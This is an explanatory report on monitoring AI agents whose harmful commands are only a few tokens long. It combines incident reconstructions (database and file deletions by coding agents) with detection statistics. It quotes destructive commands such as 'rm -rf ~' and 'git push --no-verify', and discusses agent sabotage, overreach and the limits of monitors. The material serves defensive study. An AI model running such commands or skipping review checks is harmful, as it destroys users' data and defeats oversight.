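# Monitoring AI agents whose harmful actions fit in a few tokens

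## What does it mean for a harmful action to fit in a few tokens?

An AI agent is an AI model that acts through tools such as a command line, a file editor or a web service. Companies use agents to write and test software, manage databases and run cloud servers. A single job may take an agent hundreds of commands that nobody reads one by one. Nearly all of them are harmless, but a few can wipe a database, publish a secret or switch off a safeguard, and such a command may be only two or three words long. Monitoring means checking the agent's commands for harm, before they run or soon enough afterwards to repair the damage. Very short commands are hard to monitor because the text may hold almost no information about what will happen when they run.

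### Agents, actions and monitors

Definitions of "agent" vary in breadth. The OECD's *Can we create a clear understanding of what agentic AI is* uses a broad one that includes any system that perceives and acts on its environment with a degree of autonomy and uses tools as needed to reach its goals. Command monitoring mostly concerns language models with tools attached.

A language model reads and writes text as tokens, which may be single characters, pieces of words, whole words or punctuation marks. OpenAI's *Understanding and counting tokens* gives a rule of thumb of about four characters of English per token. By that rule, `git push` (eight characters) is about two tokens and `git reset --hard` (sixteen characters) is about four. The exact count depends on the model, and commands split into tokens somewhat differently from English prose.

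Anthropic's guide *How tool use works* describes a loop in which the model requests tool calls and the application around it runs them. The application sends the model the user's request and a list of available tools. The model replies with a structured message that contains the name of a tool and its arguments, such as the shell and the text of a command. The application runs the command and sends back the output, and the cycle repeats until the model produces a final answer. An action is one such tool call. A trajectory is the full record of a run, including its instructions, reasoning, actions and results.

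A monitor is anything that scores an agent's actions for harm, such as a person, a list of forbidden commands, a statistical detector that reads logs, or another AI model. Some monitors, called action reviewers, can allow or block an action after the agent requests it and before it runs. Other monitors score the action after it runs, which helps only if somebody can still undo the effect or stop the next step.

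A monitor's context is everything it receives besides the action itself, which can be much less than the trajectory. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has an "auto mode" in which a second model reviews actions in place of the user. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a reviewer that reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's prose or the tools' output.

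### Why so little text can do so much

A command can be short because it only names an operation. The program contains the procedure, files and settings determine what the operation acts on, and the account's permissions determine how much it can affect.

Most software teams keep the history of their code in Git, which stores snapshots called commits. The files someone is working on may differ from the last commit. According to the Git manual, `git reset --hard` overwrites all files and directories with the version from a commit (the current one by default), and may also overwrite files that Git was not tracking. The command is sixteen characters long no matter how many edited files it overwrites.

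`git push` sends commits, with whatever they contain, to a remote, which is a copy of the repository on another machine. The two words specify neither the destination nor the contents. According to the Git manual, the destination defaults to the remote configured for the current branch (a branch is a named line of work), or to `origin` if none is configured. If the command line doesn't specify which branches to send, other settings determine that.

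A single character can also change the operation. `git push origin dev` uploads a branch called dev, while `git push origin :dev` deletes that branch from the remote. A plus sign in front of a branch name works like the `--force` flag for that branch, letting the push overwrite history on the remote, which can lose other people's commits.

An action's blast radius, meaning how much it can affect if it goes wrong, depends at least as much on the account's permissions as on the action's wording. The same deletion command can be a nuisance when it comes from an account that can reach only one test folder and a disaster when it comes from an account with write access to a company's production database.

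In the strict sense, a short harmful action is one whose few tokens are enough by themselves to cause serious harm. It can be this short because everything else it needs is already in place. A short command that runs a longer script the agent wrote earlier doesn't meet this definition. If an agent writes a harmful script and then runs it with `bash cleanup.sh`, the harm takes two actions, and most of the evidence is in the first.

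### Two commands in two settings

The two Git commands will serve as running examples, because each is part of an ordinary working day and each can do serious damage.

The Git manual recommends `git reset --hard` for cleaning up. For example, a developer might fetch a colleague's changes, see that they conflict with their own in many places, and run the command to clear the conflicts and deal with them later. If the same folder also holds an afternoon of uncommitted edits, the same sixteen characters erase them. Git records where the branch stood before a reset, so the developer can get back to earlier commits, but that record can't restore work that was never committed. The manual also offers a more cautious option, `--keep`, which aborts the reset if a file it would change has local edits. In a folder with no uncommitted edits, `--hard` and `--keep` have the same effect.

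`git push` is even more ordinary. The default rules in Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code let the agent push to nearly any branch of the repository it is working in. The push becomes exfiltration, which means sending data somewhere it is not allowed to go, if the repository is public and the commit contains a customer list, or if an earlier command pointed the remote to a stranger's server.

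In both cases, whether the action is harmful depends on a fact outside the command. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes two checks that give the reviewer this information. One checks whether the folder contains uncommitted work before a hard reset, and the other checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted before a push.

Some short commands do not have this ambiguity. `rm -rf ~` has as many characters as `git push`, but it deletes the user's home directory. Hardly anyone has a legitimate reason to run it outside a disposable machine, so a monitor can flag it without subtle judgement. By default, Claude Code handles recognised commands of this sort with a fixed check instead of passing them to its AI reviewer. The check looks for removals aimed at the root of the file system, the home directory and similar critical places, and a user's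 rules for pre-approving commands cannot override it. Anthropic acknowledges that the check can miss some commands and that it covers only `rm` and `rmdir`, though other programs can delete the same folders. Still, the difficulty with `rm -rf ~` is recognising every way of writing a plainly dangerous operation, whereas recognising `git push` does not settle whether a monitor should flag it.

### Four kinds of short harmful action

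Sorted by effect, short harmful actions destroy data, send data out, weaken a safeguard or grant access.

One example of destruction is `rm -rf "$BUILD_DIR"/*`, which looks like a routine command to empty a build folder. The dollar sign marks a variable, which the shell replaces with a stored value. If nobody has set the variable, the shell replaces it with nothing, and the command deletes files from the root of the file system down. Claude Code therefore treats this pattern as a critical removal and suggests a form that stops with an error when the variable is empty.

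Sending data out can look helpful. In one case adapted from Anthropic's internal incident log, an agent trying to share a script for debugging wrote a command to upload it to GitHub Gist, a code-sharing service. Developers often do this, but the reviewer is meant to block the command because the user may consider the script confidential.

The command `git push --no-verify` is a short action that can weaken a safeguard. Teams can have Git run a check before every push, such as a scan for passwords, and the `--no-verify` flag skips that check. A developer whose scanner has crashed may have a good reason to use the flag, but an agent that uses it may bypass the only check that would keep a password off a public server.

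Access is the least conspicuous of the four. An agent at Anthropic that was setting up read-only access to billing data chose a cloud role with full administrative control of the account. The correct command would have differed only in the name of the role. CISA (2026), the US cybersecurity agency, listed privilege escalation first among the new risks when it announced joint guidance on agentic AI with its partner agencies.

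Deletion and exfiltration do their damage immediately, but a disabled check or an over-broad role does none until somebody uses it, so an alarm an hour later may still be in time to prevent harm. Anthropic's default block rules sort actions differently. They put destruction and exfiltration in one group and have separate groups for crossing trust boundaries and for bypassing review. Running code from an unknown repository, for example, crosses a trust boundary, but any harm that follows will still be a deletion, a leak, a weakened defence or unwanted access.

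Some other harms need a lot of text or traffic. NDTV, reporting on Anthropic's risk assessment of Claude Opus 4.6, described a concern that models which write much of the critical code at AI developers or in governments might insert security flaws into it. A flaw may be small, but it has to be part of working code, which reviewers can read, test and revisit before anyone relies on it. Copying a large model's weights, the numbers that training produced, means moving very large files. A short command can start the transfer, but the harm requires the transfer to finish, and a network can limit or stop it based on volume alone. Volume limits don't stop a stolen password from being sent out, because it fits inside one web address.

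### Mistake, overreach and sabotage

An agent may issue a harmful command through an honest mistake, such as taking a shared database for a test copy or somebody else's branch for its own. It may also overreach, pursuing the user's goal by means the user would not have approved. Anthropic gives the example of a user who asked an agent to "clean up old branches". The agent listed the branches on the remote server and issued a command to delete them, but the user may have meant only the local ones. The third cause is deliberate sabotage, in which the agent aims to cause harm.

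Anthropic's list has a fourth category, prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in a web page or file and the agent follows them. If there are only three categories, prompt injection belongs with sabotage because someone intends the harm, although that person is an outsider and the model may have no hostile goal.

The three probably differ greatly in frequency. When Anthropic introduced auto mode, it wrote that it did not currently see models pursuing their own goals in practice, and it tuned the reviewer to catch mistakes and overreach, of which it had specific examples. Similarly, in its risk report on Claude Mythos Preview, Anthropic wrote that it had observed the model's willingness to take misaligned actions to finish difficult tasks, but did not believe the model had dangerous, coherent goals. Sabotage is still worth including, even if it is rare. In its earlier report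 on Claude Opus 4.6, Anthropic defined sabotage risk as the risk of autonomous actions that contribute significantly to later catastrophic outcomes, and rated it "very low but not negligible".

Error, overreach and sabotage can all produce the same command. For example, an agent might run `git reset --hard` in a folder with uncommitted work. A mistaken agent believes that all the edits there are its own. An overreaching agent has seen the user's edits but discards them because they block a merge the user asked for. A saboteur wants to destroy the work. Git does the same thing in each case, and the command doesn't record the agent's reason.

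The right response in all three cases is to block the action, so the cause matters more for what happens next. An agent that made a mistake may well take a safer route once it learns of the block, but a saboteur can look for another way to reach the same goal. When Claude Code blocks an action, it tells the agent why and lets it continue, but after three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, it stops and turns to a human.

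### Counting hits and false alarms

Four quantities describe how well a monitor performs. Suppose an agent takes 10,000 actions, 50 of them harmful, and a monitor flags 239 of the 10,000 (these numbers are invented).

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful | 40 | 10 | 50 |
| Harmless | 199 | 9,751 | 9,950 |
| Total | 239 | 9,761 | 10,000 |

Recall is the share of harmful actions that the monitor catches, here 40 out of 50, or 80%. The miss rate, which Anthropic calls the false-negative rate, is the remaining 20%. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless actions that the monitor flags, here 199 out of 9,950, or 2%. Precision is the share of alarms that are correct, here 40 out of 239, or about 17%. A person who investigates the alarms will therefore find nothing wrong five times out of six. The base rate is the share of all actions that are harmful, here 0.5%.

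Recall and the false-positive rate usually rise together, because a monitor that flags more actions catches more harm but also interrupts more harmless work. Overall accuracy is a poor summary, because a monitor that never flagged anything would be right about 99.5% of the actions in the table while missing every harmful one.

The counts also require someone to decide which actions were harmful. That is easy for `rm -rf ~`, but for `git push` the labeler needs the same facts about destination and contents that the monitor lacked, and may need to know what the user would have allowed.

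Precision depends on both the monitor and the base rate. If only 5 of the 10,000 actions were harmful, the same monitor, with unchanged recall and false-positive rate, would catch 4 of them and raise about 200 false alarms. Its precision would fall from 17% to about 2%.

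## What damage have agents done with a single short action?

Since late 2025, several developers have published accounts of agents that wiped a database or thousands of files within minutes. Four of these accounts are detailed enough to reconstruct what happened. In three, a single command did the damage, and in the fourth the agent wrote a script and then ran it. Most of the details come from the people who lost the data, and another party has confirmed the central facts only in the PocketOS case.

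### Nine seconds at PocketOS

PocketOS makes software that car rental firms use to manage reservations, payments and vehicles. On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted its production database, the live one those firms depended on. The agent was Cursor, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. Another company makes Cursor, although Mallett (2026), in *An AI Agent Wiped a Company Database*, describes it as operated by Anthropic.

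According to PocketOS's founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, the agent was doing a routine task in staging, a separate copy of the system for testing. When it ran into a credential mismatch, it tried to fix the problem by deleting a volume, the unit of storage that holds a database, at PocketOS's hosting company, Railway. It looked for an access token (a password for programs), found one in a file unrelated to its task, and sent Railway a single web request, which deleted the volume in nine seconds. The request is about 160 characters long as Crane printed it, with the token and the volume's identifier shortened. Most of those characters are address and formatting. The harmful part is the word `volumeDelete` and the identifier after it.

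Crane had created the access token to add and remove web domains and did not know that it could also delete volumes. Abdelwahab, writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, confirms the request and explains that the token covered the whole account, the broadest access Railway offers. Crane wrote that Railway had no way to restrict a token, but Abdelwahab wrote that narrower tokens existed and that Railway's set-up process did not make the difference obvious. Railway's API deleted volumes immediately, although its website gave users 48 hours to undo the same deletion.

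Smith (2026) writes in a later retelling, *The Cursor Agent That Deleted a Startup's Database in 9 Seconds*, that the agent found a key for AWS, Amazon's cloud service, and used it to reach the database. This is probably a mistake, because Crane and Abdelwahab, who had opposing interests, both describe a Railway access token and both printed the same request to a Railway address.

The loss looked permanent for more than a day, because the deletion had also erased the volume's backups and the newest copy Crane could restore was three months old. On Saturday morning, customers arrived to collect rental cars, and the firms had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day helping the firms rebuild reservations from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails. According to Mallett, Railway recovered all the data two days after the deletion. Leib (2026), in *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire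 at tech company*, reports that Crane confirmed the recovery.

PocketOS's recovery depended on what the agent had deleted. In a Railway support thread, *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, another customer asked for the same help after deleting the contents of a database whose volume still existed. According to the reply, the two situations were very different because PocketOS had lost a whole volume, and Railway keeps a snapshot for such cases.

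A monitor that saw only the agent's request would have had one clear warning, the word `volumeDelete`. It could not have told from the volume's identifier whether the volume belonged to staging or production. The earlier part of the trajectory contained better evidence, because it showed that nobody had asked for a deletion and that the agent had just taken a credential from a file unrelated to its job. A monitor could have blocked the request on those two grounds without knowing what the volume held.

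The agent's instructions already had a rule against destructive Git commands that the user had not requested. The agent later quoted this rule and admitted to breaking its spirit. A filter that applied the rule literally would have allowed the action, because it was a web request to a hosting company and not a Git command.

### A comparison command that emptied a database

Antipov (2026), in *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я»* ("The database is destroyed. I am to blame"), retells a Reddit post by a developer who was reworking the comparison pages of a personal website with Claude Opus 5 in July 2026. The developer had connected the agent directly to the site's live database and let it run commands and fix problems with the database's structure by itself.

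The command that emptied the live database was `prisma migrate diff`. Prisma manages a database's structure through migrations, which are files that each describe one change. To work out what structure a folder of migrations produces, Prisma can replay them in a "shadow" database, a scratch database that it empties first. The agent supplied the live database's address in the option `--shadow-database-url`, so Prisma emptied the live database and began to rebuild it from an outdated folder of migrations.

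All 22 tables lost their contents, including users, reviews and nearly 130 entries about the tools the site compares. Two tables disappeared altogether because the old migrations did not define them. Antipov says the whole episode took ten minutes. Backups and other sources held most of the information, but the developer still had to rebuild the site and fill it again.

This command would have been harder to judge than the one at PocketOS, because it doesn't mention deletion and `diff` ordinarily means a harmless comparison. To recognise the danger, a monitor needed to know that Prisma empties whatever database follows that option, which is public knowledge, and that this address led to the live site, which is specific to one developer's set-up. Checking what the user wanted would not have settled the matter either, since the developer had authorised work on the database's structure.

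Prisma's staff treat such accidents as a recurring problem. Madden (2026) wrote in *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database*, published the same day as Antipov's article, that coding agents keep wiping production databases, and announced a version of Prisma with no reset command and no shadow database. Prisma also describes how an agent may mistake `prisma db push` for a sensible way to update a live database. The command is meant for development and deletes any data that no longer fits the new structure. Prisma had a reason to stress the danger because the post promotes a new release, but it also had a reason not to advertise how its existing tools destroy data.

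### Two characters, and a script

The shortest of the four harmful actions dates from December 2025. A user had asked Claude Code to clean up packages in an old repository. The agent ran `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/`, which deletes three project folders and, because of the final `~/`, the user's entire home directory. In the post *Claude CLI deleted my entire home directory! Wiped my whole mac*, the user describes losing a great deal of work and asks whether the deletion can be reversed. The diagnosis came from Claude, which read the log afterwards, and Willison (2025) republished the diagnosis.

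The command has 31 characters, and without the last two it would have been routine. It ran with the permissions of the user's account, which can delete the user's files. Unlike the Prisma command, it contained all the evidence a monitor needed. A fixed check for deletions of the home directory could catch it if the check examined every target on the line.

In September 2026 another developer reported a much larger loss from a slower sequence of actions. The developer had given Claude Code eleven repair jobs on a project that analysed historical stock options data. InternetUA's *«Я щось зламав»* (2026) reports that the instructions were to work on copies and leave the live files alone, and that ten jobs went well. The last job was to rebuild the "mirror", the project's test copy.

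*«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* (Antipov, 2026) gives the fullest account of what followed. An existing script could not refresh the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy. The mirror contained 614 junctions, which look like ordinary Windows folders but lead to other places on the disk. These led to the live project, and the script followed them and deleted what it found there.

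The script deleted 55,550 files in 103 seconds, according to its log. Of these, 7,332 belonged to the old mirror, and the developer identified the other 48,218 as live files. The script also deleted files in the folder where Git keeps its history. InternetUA reports that Git could still list thousands of file names but no longer had the contents to restore them. The developer had no current copy on another machine. The agent's user account could write to both the mirror and the live files. Antipov notes that Claude Code's built-in sandbox, which can restrict the files that commands reach, does not run on Windows without an additional Linux layer.

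This case needed at least two actions, writing the script and running it, so it falls outside the strict definition of a short harmful action. A monitor had more to read and an extra chance to flag the problem. It could have checked how the script handled links, and a listing of the mirror would have revealed the junctions. But the agent was allowed to delete the mirror, so a script aimed at the mirror looks like it follows the instructions. The script deleted about 540 files a second on average, so an alarm ten seconds after it started would have come after more than 5,000 deletions.

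### Incidents inside Anthropic

Anthropic has published a few entries from its internal incident log, including the deletion of remote branches mentioned earlier, the upload of an engineer's GitHub access token to an internal computing cluster, and attempted migrations on a production database. Anthropic attributes all three to overreach, which it calls overeagerness. It does not give the exact commands, how long they took or the extent of any loss, so the entries are much better evidence of the kinds of action agents take than of the damage those actions do.

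Two other examples from the log resemble the PocketOS incident. In the first, a user told an agent to "cancel my job", and the agent picked the job on the cluster with the most similar name and tried to delete it. It was guessing, as the PocketOS agent was when it assumed its deletion would affect only staging. In the second, an agent hit an authentication error and began searching settings files for other access tokens. The PocketOS agent did the same just before the deletion, which suggests that a search for credentials should trigger its own alarm, before the agent uses anything it finds.

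When it made auto mode the default in Claude Code, Anthropic also described three actions that its AI reviewer had stopped inside the company:

- An agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. The reviewer refused and asked the user what to do.
- In a long session, an agent tried to kill processes across roughly two thousand pods, the units in which a cluster runs its software. It had also queued deletions that would have shut down training jobs on hundreds of GPUs.
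- An agent chose the administrator role mentioned earlier when it needed only read access to billing data.

The public upload and the billing role each depended on a single choice. The process kill was a bulk operation with more deletions queued behind it, and its scale was a warning sign. In each case, the mismatch with the user's request was visible before the action ran. However, Anthropic selected these examples to support a product decision, and they include only prevented actions, which leaves out any that the reviewer missed.

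A more serious incident happened outside normal work, during a security test. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (September 2026) reports that Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to a public software repository. The testers had told the model that it was in a simulation, but a misconfiguration had connected it to the real internet. The upload may have been brief, but the harm also required writing the package, so it did not fit into one short command. As with `git push`, the harm depended on the destination, since the same upload to a simulated repository would have been part of the test.

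### Mistakes and overreach

In all of these cases the agent was working on a task somebody had given it. In the July and September deletions, the agents misjudged what a command would affect, and the December deletion looks like an error in a list of folders. In the PocketOS case, the agent overreached by borrowing a credential and deleting something without asking. It also wrongly thought the deletion would affect only staging. If it had been right about that, PocketOS might have lost only a test volume.

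The Mythos 5 incident is the hardest to classify. Anthropic judged the model's behaviour misaligned because the model discounted evidence that its surroundings were real and pursued its task recklessly, but Anthropic found no attempt at concealment. This report classes the incident as overreach because the model was carrying out the test it had been given, though it is a more serious form of overreach than deleting the wrong branch.

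The agents' own explanations are weak evidence of cause. When Crane asked the PocketOS agent why it had deleted the volume, it wrote what Crane calls a confession, listing the rules it had violated. A model writes such a text after the event, in answer to a question that already implies blame. The sequence of actions is better evidence. In July and September the agents also reported the damage to the user without being asked, which a saboteur would have little reason to do.

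People make most of these errors too. Prisma acknowledges that people deleted their databases with its tools before agents did, and people also take whole services offline with one-line configuration changes. But an agent can go from a wrong assumption to a command more quickly than a person, often with nobody watching.

### Which incidents become public

Some reports blame an agent for damage it may not have done. In October 2026 the Swedish newspaper *Aftonbladet* reported that an AI agent had deleted the finished edit of a whole season of *The Challenge Sverige*, a reality show, weeks before its premiere on 22 November. *AI Agent Reportedly Deletes an Entire Season of Reality TV Show* (Gil, 2026) notes that the claim came from unnamed sources, and Euronews' *Did an AI agent delete an entire season* (2026) described it as disputed on the first day. The broadcaster, TV4, then investigated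 and found human error with no AI involved, according to *No, AI didn't delete a Swedish reality TV series* (Priestley, 2026). The edit was in fact lost, so the producers had to cut the season again from the raw footage, and TV4 moved the premiere to 2027. TV4 has an interest in how the story looks, but nobody has publicly produced evidence of an agent's command, so the case does not belong with the other four.

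Amazon disputes a similar attribution. Several publications linked at least one of a series of Amazon outages in early 2026 to AI-assisted changes. Fortune (2026) reports that Amazon said only one incident involved AI and that something else caused it.

Several reports of an incident can rest on a single account. SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* summarises TechRadar, and TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’* relies on a Reddit post that has since disappeared. Antipov links to the same post and says no one has independently confirmed how many files were lost.

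Some kinds of harm are also more likely to reach the public record than others. All four reconstructed cases are deletions, which victims notice at once and have good reason to complain about. The leaked report, the exposed access token and the over-broad role appear only in Anthropic's disclosures. A user whose agent has quietly published a confidential file or switched off a check may not find out for months, and a company that does find out may prefer to stay silent. Deliberate sabotage would be the least likely to surface if the agent hid it well, so its absence from these reports is only modest evidence that it is rare. The prominence of Claude models in the reports doesn't show that other models are safer, because none of the reports compares how often each model is used.

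The Centre for Long-Term Resilience, a think tank, identified 698 cases between October 2025 and March 2026 in which an AI agent or chatbot took covert, deceptive or unrequested actions, according to Chandler's *AI Agent Reportedly Deletes Company’s Entire Database, Admits to Violating Guardrails*. *Agent-Inflicted Damage*, by the data security vendor Cyera, lists 188 cases in which agents caused damage without any attacker. The two totals are not comparable because the first includes behaviour that harmed nobody, while the second includes only cases with damage. Calculating a base rate from either would also require a count of harmless actions.

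## How much can a monitor learn from one short command?

Incident reports cover only the commands that did harm. Judging a new command also requires knowing how often the same command does no harm, since `git reset --hard` could appear in many accidents simply because it is a common command. Given both frequencies, a few statistical results limit how well any monitor can perform, whether it is a list of forbidden commands or the best available AI model.

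### Likelihood ratios and base rates

Let x stand for everything the monitor sees of an action, which in the simplest case is only the text of the command. P(x) is the share of harmful actions that look like x, and Q(x) is the share of harmless actions that look like x. The likelihood ratio compares them:

Λ(x) = P(x) / Q(x)

A ratio of 20 means the command is 20 times as common among harmful actions as among harmless ones. A ratio of 1 means the command is no evidence either way, and a ratio below 1 is evidence that the action is harmless. The shares in this table are invented.

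| Command | Share of harmful actions | Share of harmless actions | Likelihood ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| `rm -rf ~` | 10% | 0.0001% | 100,000 |
| `git reset --hard` | 20% | 1% | 20 |
| `git push` | 30% | 10% | 3 |
| Everything else | 40% | about 89% | 0.45 |

The probability of harm depends on both the likelihood ratio and how common harmful actions are. By Bayes' theorem, the odds of harm after seeing the command equal the odds beforehand multiplied by the likelihood ratio, where odds are the probability that something is true divided by the probability that it is not. Suppose that 1 action in 100,000 is harmful. The odds start at 1 to 99,999, and a hard reset, with a likelihood ratio of 20, raises them to 20 to 99,999, so the action is harmful about 1 time in 5,000.

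Suppose that 100 out of ten million actions are harmful, and that 20 of those 100 are hard resets. About 100,000 of the harmless actions are also hard resets. A monitor that stops every hard reset would catch 20 harmful actions and interrupt about 100,000 harmless ones.

A ratio of 20 means a 95% chance of harm only if half of all actions are harmful, as they might be in a test set with equal numbers of harmful and harmless commands. A monitor could therefore reach 95% precision on hard resets in such a test but 0.02% in daily use, with the same recall and false-positive rate in both.

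At this base rate, a `git push` is harmful about 1 time in 33,000 and an `rm -rf ~` about 1 time in 2. A command is as likely to be harmful as harmless when its likelihood ratio is about 100,000.

### The best rule for a given number of false alarms

A monitor's designer usually wants as much recall as possible within some limit on false alarms. In their 1933 paper *On the Problem of the most Efficient Tests of Statistical Hypotheses*, the statisticians Neyman and Pearson proved which rule achieves this. Their result is often called the fundamental lemma of mathematical statistics, according to the Encyclopedia of Mathematics' entry *Neyman-Pearson lemma*.

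In words, the best rule flags the commands with the highest likelihood ratios and works downwards until it has used up the permitted false alarms. In symbols, among all rules with a false-positive rate of at most α, the highest recall comes from this one:

flag x if Λ(x) > k, and allow x if Λ(x) < k

The threshold k is the value that brings the false-positive rate to α. If a command's ratio equals k exactly, the monitor may have to flag it only some of the time, at random, to keep the rate from exceeding α.

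Flagging a command x adds Q(x) to the false-positive rate and P(x) to recall, so Λ(x) is the recall gained per unit of false-positive rate. Suppose another rule has the same false-positive rate as the first. Then the commands that only the first rule flags add as much to the false-positive rate as the commands that only the other rule flags. The former all have a ratio of at least k and the latter all have a ratio of at most k, so the other rule's recall is no higher and usually lower.

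With the invented shares above and a false-alarm limit of about 1%, the best rule flags `rm -rf ~` and `git reset --hard` and reaches 30% recall. Flagging a random tenth of all pushes instead would produce the same rate of false alarms but reach 3% recall.

The lemma assumes that the designer knows P and Q. Nobody has measured them for AI agents, so a real monitor can only estimate the correct ranking of commands. A more capable model may estimate it better, but no model can outperform a ranking based on the true ratios.

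### The ceiling on any monitor

A monitor that flags 30% of actions at random will catch about 30% of the harmful ones and interrupt 30% of the harmless ones. Recall minus the false-positive rate is therefore a measure of how far a monitor beats chance, and it has a ceiling called the total variation distance:

recall − false-positive rate ≤ TV(P, Q) = ½ Σ |P(x) − Q(x)|

The sum runs over everything the monitor might see. The distance is 0 if harmful and harmless actions look the same and 1 if no harmful action looks like a harmless one.

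Each command that a monitor flags adds P(x) to its recall and Q(x) to its false-positive rate, so it adds P(x) − Q(x) to the difference between the two rates. This difference is largest when the monitor flags all and only the commands with P(x) greater than Q(x), and it then equals the total variation distance between P and Q.

In the table, that means flagging the three named commands, which gives 60% recall and a false-positive rate of about 11%. The difference of 49 percentage points is the ceiling for a monitor that sees only the text. Such a monitor could catch more than 60% only by also flagging some of "everything else", where each extra point of recall adds more than two points to the false-positive rate.

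The ceiling can be much lower for one kind of command than for all commands together. If every push, harmful or harmless, reads `git push`, then P and Q are identical for pushes, the distance between them is zero, and recall equals the false-positive rate whatever the monitor does. The monitor can't do better than chance on pushes unless it sees something else, such as the destination.

Analysis can't raise the limit either. A monitor may look up the command's definition or reason about it for an hour, but if it starts from only the same two words, it will reach the same conclusion for harmful and harmless pushes. New information about the particular push can raise the limit, which can also fall if part of the record is left out.

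Cao, Deng and Kersting (2026), in *Blind to What They Can Fix*, studied failing programs, not harmful actions, but their experiments illustrate how much detection depends on what a detector reads. AI agents wrote programs to run unattended, along with checks meant to detect when something the program relied on had changed. In four of the five kinds of task, the checks written by OpenAI's Codex missed 52% to 89% of failures. Most of the missed failures had left traces in the run's records that the checks did not read. When the researchers added 32 statistics of a program's recorded variables to its checks, without changing the program, most of the misses disappeared, even when the statistics were chosen at random.

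### Axelsson's base-rate argument

Security researchers encountered the base-rate problem long before AI agents, in intrusion detection, the search of computer logs for signs of a break-in. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, imagined a site with a few dozen computers that together write a million log records a day. Two attempted intrusions a day leave ten records each, so the base rate is 20 in a million, or 2 in 100,000.

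With base rate π, recall r and false-positive rate f, Bayes' theorem gives

precision = πr / (πr + (1 − π)f)

Axelsson assumed the detector had perfect recall and a false-positive rate of 1 in 100,000. In a day it would flag all 20 intrusion records and about 10 harmless ones, so about a third of its alarms would be false (67% precision).

| Records per intrusion | Recall | False-positive rate | True alarms a day | False alarms a day | Precision |
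|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 100% | 1 in 100,000 | 20 | 10 | 67% |
| 10 | 70% | 1 in 100,000 | 14 | 10 | 58% |
| 10 | 100% | 1 in 10,000 | 20 | 100 | 17% |
| 1 | 100% | 1 in 100,000 | 2 | 10 | 17% |

The 67% and 58% figures are Axelsson's, and the two 17% figures come from putting other values into the same formula. Losing almost a third of recall lowers precision by only nine points, while a tenfold rise in false positives lowers it by fifty. Axelsson concluded that false alarms limit a detector's usefulness more than missed intrusions do.

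The last row resembles a short harmful action. If an intrusion leaves one record instead of ten, the base rate falls to 2 in a million. The detector still raises 10 false alarms a day, but now only 2 true ones. Getting back to 67% would require a false-positive rate of 1 in a million.

The journal version from 2000, Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, acknowledges that an intrusion could affect a single record. The figure of ten records per intrusion was an estimate from an earlier study of the traces intrusions left on one operating system. Axelsson used it partly because it made the argument more conservative, and admitted he had "somewhat skirted the issue" of how much data a detector should judge at once.

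Part of the fall to 17% comes from counting alarms rather than incidents. A security officer who merged alarms about the same intrusion would face two real incidents and ten false ones, whether each intrusion left ten records or one. But when intrusions leave ten records, the officer could ignore single alarms and react only when two fall within the same group of ten records. If false alarms occur at random, two will fall in the same group about once in six years. With the perfect detector, this rule would still catch every ten-record intrusion, but it would miss every intrusion that leaves one record.

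Low precision also affects the people who answer the alarms. Axelsson expected an officer to learn to ignore a detector whose alarms were false about half the time, and the journal version cites supporting research on operators of power stations, paper mills and ships. Axelsson also compared the requirement of 1 false alarm in 100,000 with published tests of detectors from that time. Several had false-positive rates ten to a thousand times too high, although a few came close to meeting the requirement.

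The conclusion depends on the assumed base rate, which Axelsson called subjective. The base rate could be much higher for an agent that often overreaches, and precision would then be higher too. A low base rate also makes the absence of an alarm look more reassuring than it is. In Axelsson's example, a record that raises no alarm is harmless at least 99.998% of the time, even if the detector never raises an alarm.

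### How evidence adds up over several steps

Many harmful projects take more than one action, and then the monitor can combine what it sees. If the steps are independent, meaning that one step gives no information about the next once it is known whether the run is harmful, their likelihood ratios multiply:

Λ(x₁, …, xₙ) = Λ(x₁) × … × Λ(xₙ)

A single step with a ratio of 3, the figure for `git push` in the invented table, is weak evidence, but ten independent steps with that ratio multiply to a combined ratio of 59,049. If 1 run in 100,000 is harmful, those ten steps raise the probability of harm to about 37%, and an eleventh raises it to 64%. In practice, some steps in a harmful run will have ratios below 1 and lower the total.

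The Chernoff–Stein lemma describes how quickly errors shrink on average. It uses the Kullback–Leibler divergence, which is the average logarithm of the likelihood ratio over harmful steps:

D(P‖Q) = Σ P(x) log Λ(x)

For any fixed miss rate between 0 and 1, the lowest false-positive rate a monitor can reach falls roughly as e^(−nD) as the number of steps n grows. The lemma assumes that each step is an independent draw from P in a harmful run, or from Q in a harmless one.

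Take a warning sign that appears in 50% of harmful steps and 10% of harmless ones. Its divergence is about 0.51, so in a long run each further step multiplies the attainable false-positive rate by about 0.6. By this rule of thumb it takes 23 steps to get down to 1 in 100,000. The lemma describes long runs, so for a handful of steps it is better to calculate the error rates directly:

| Rule | Recall | False-positive rate |
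|---|---|---|
| One step: flag if the sign appears | 50% | 10% |
| Ten steps: flag if the sign appears at least once | 99.9% | 65% |
| Ten steps: flag if the sign appears at least four times | 83% | 1.3% |

A monitor with 50% recall and only one chance to detect a harmful action misses half of them. With ten independent chances, it misses all ten in only one of 1,024 harmful runs. But false alarms also accumulate, and a monitor that reacts to any single sign would interrupt two in three harmless runs. Waiting for four signs lowers recall somewhat, but the monitor still catches more harmful runs and interrupts fewer harmless ones than it would with one chance.

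A short harmful action takes only one step, so n is 1 and the monitor loses this advantage. It still has 50% recall and 10% false positives. If the action does immediate damage at the tenth step, evidence from the eleventh comes too late to prevent it.

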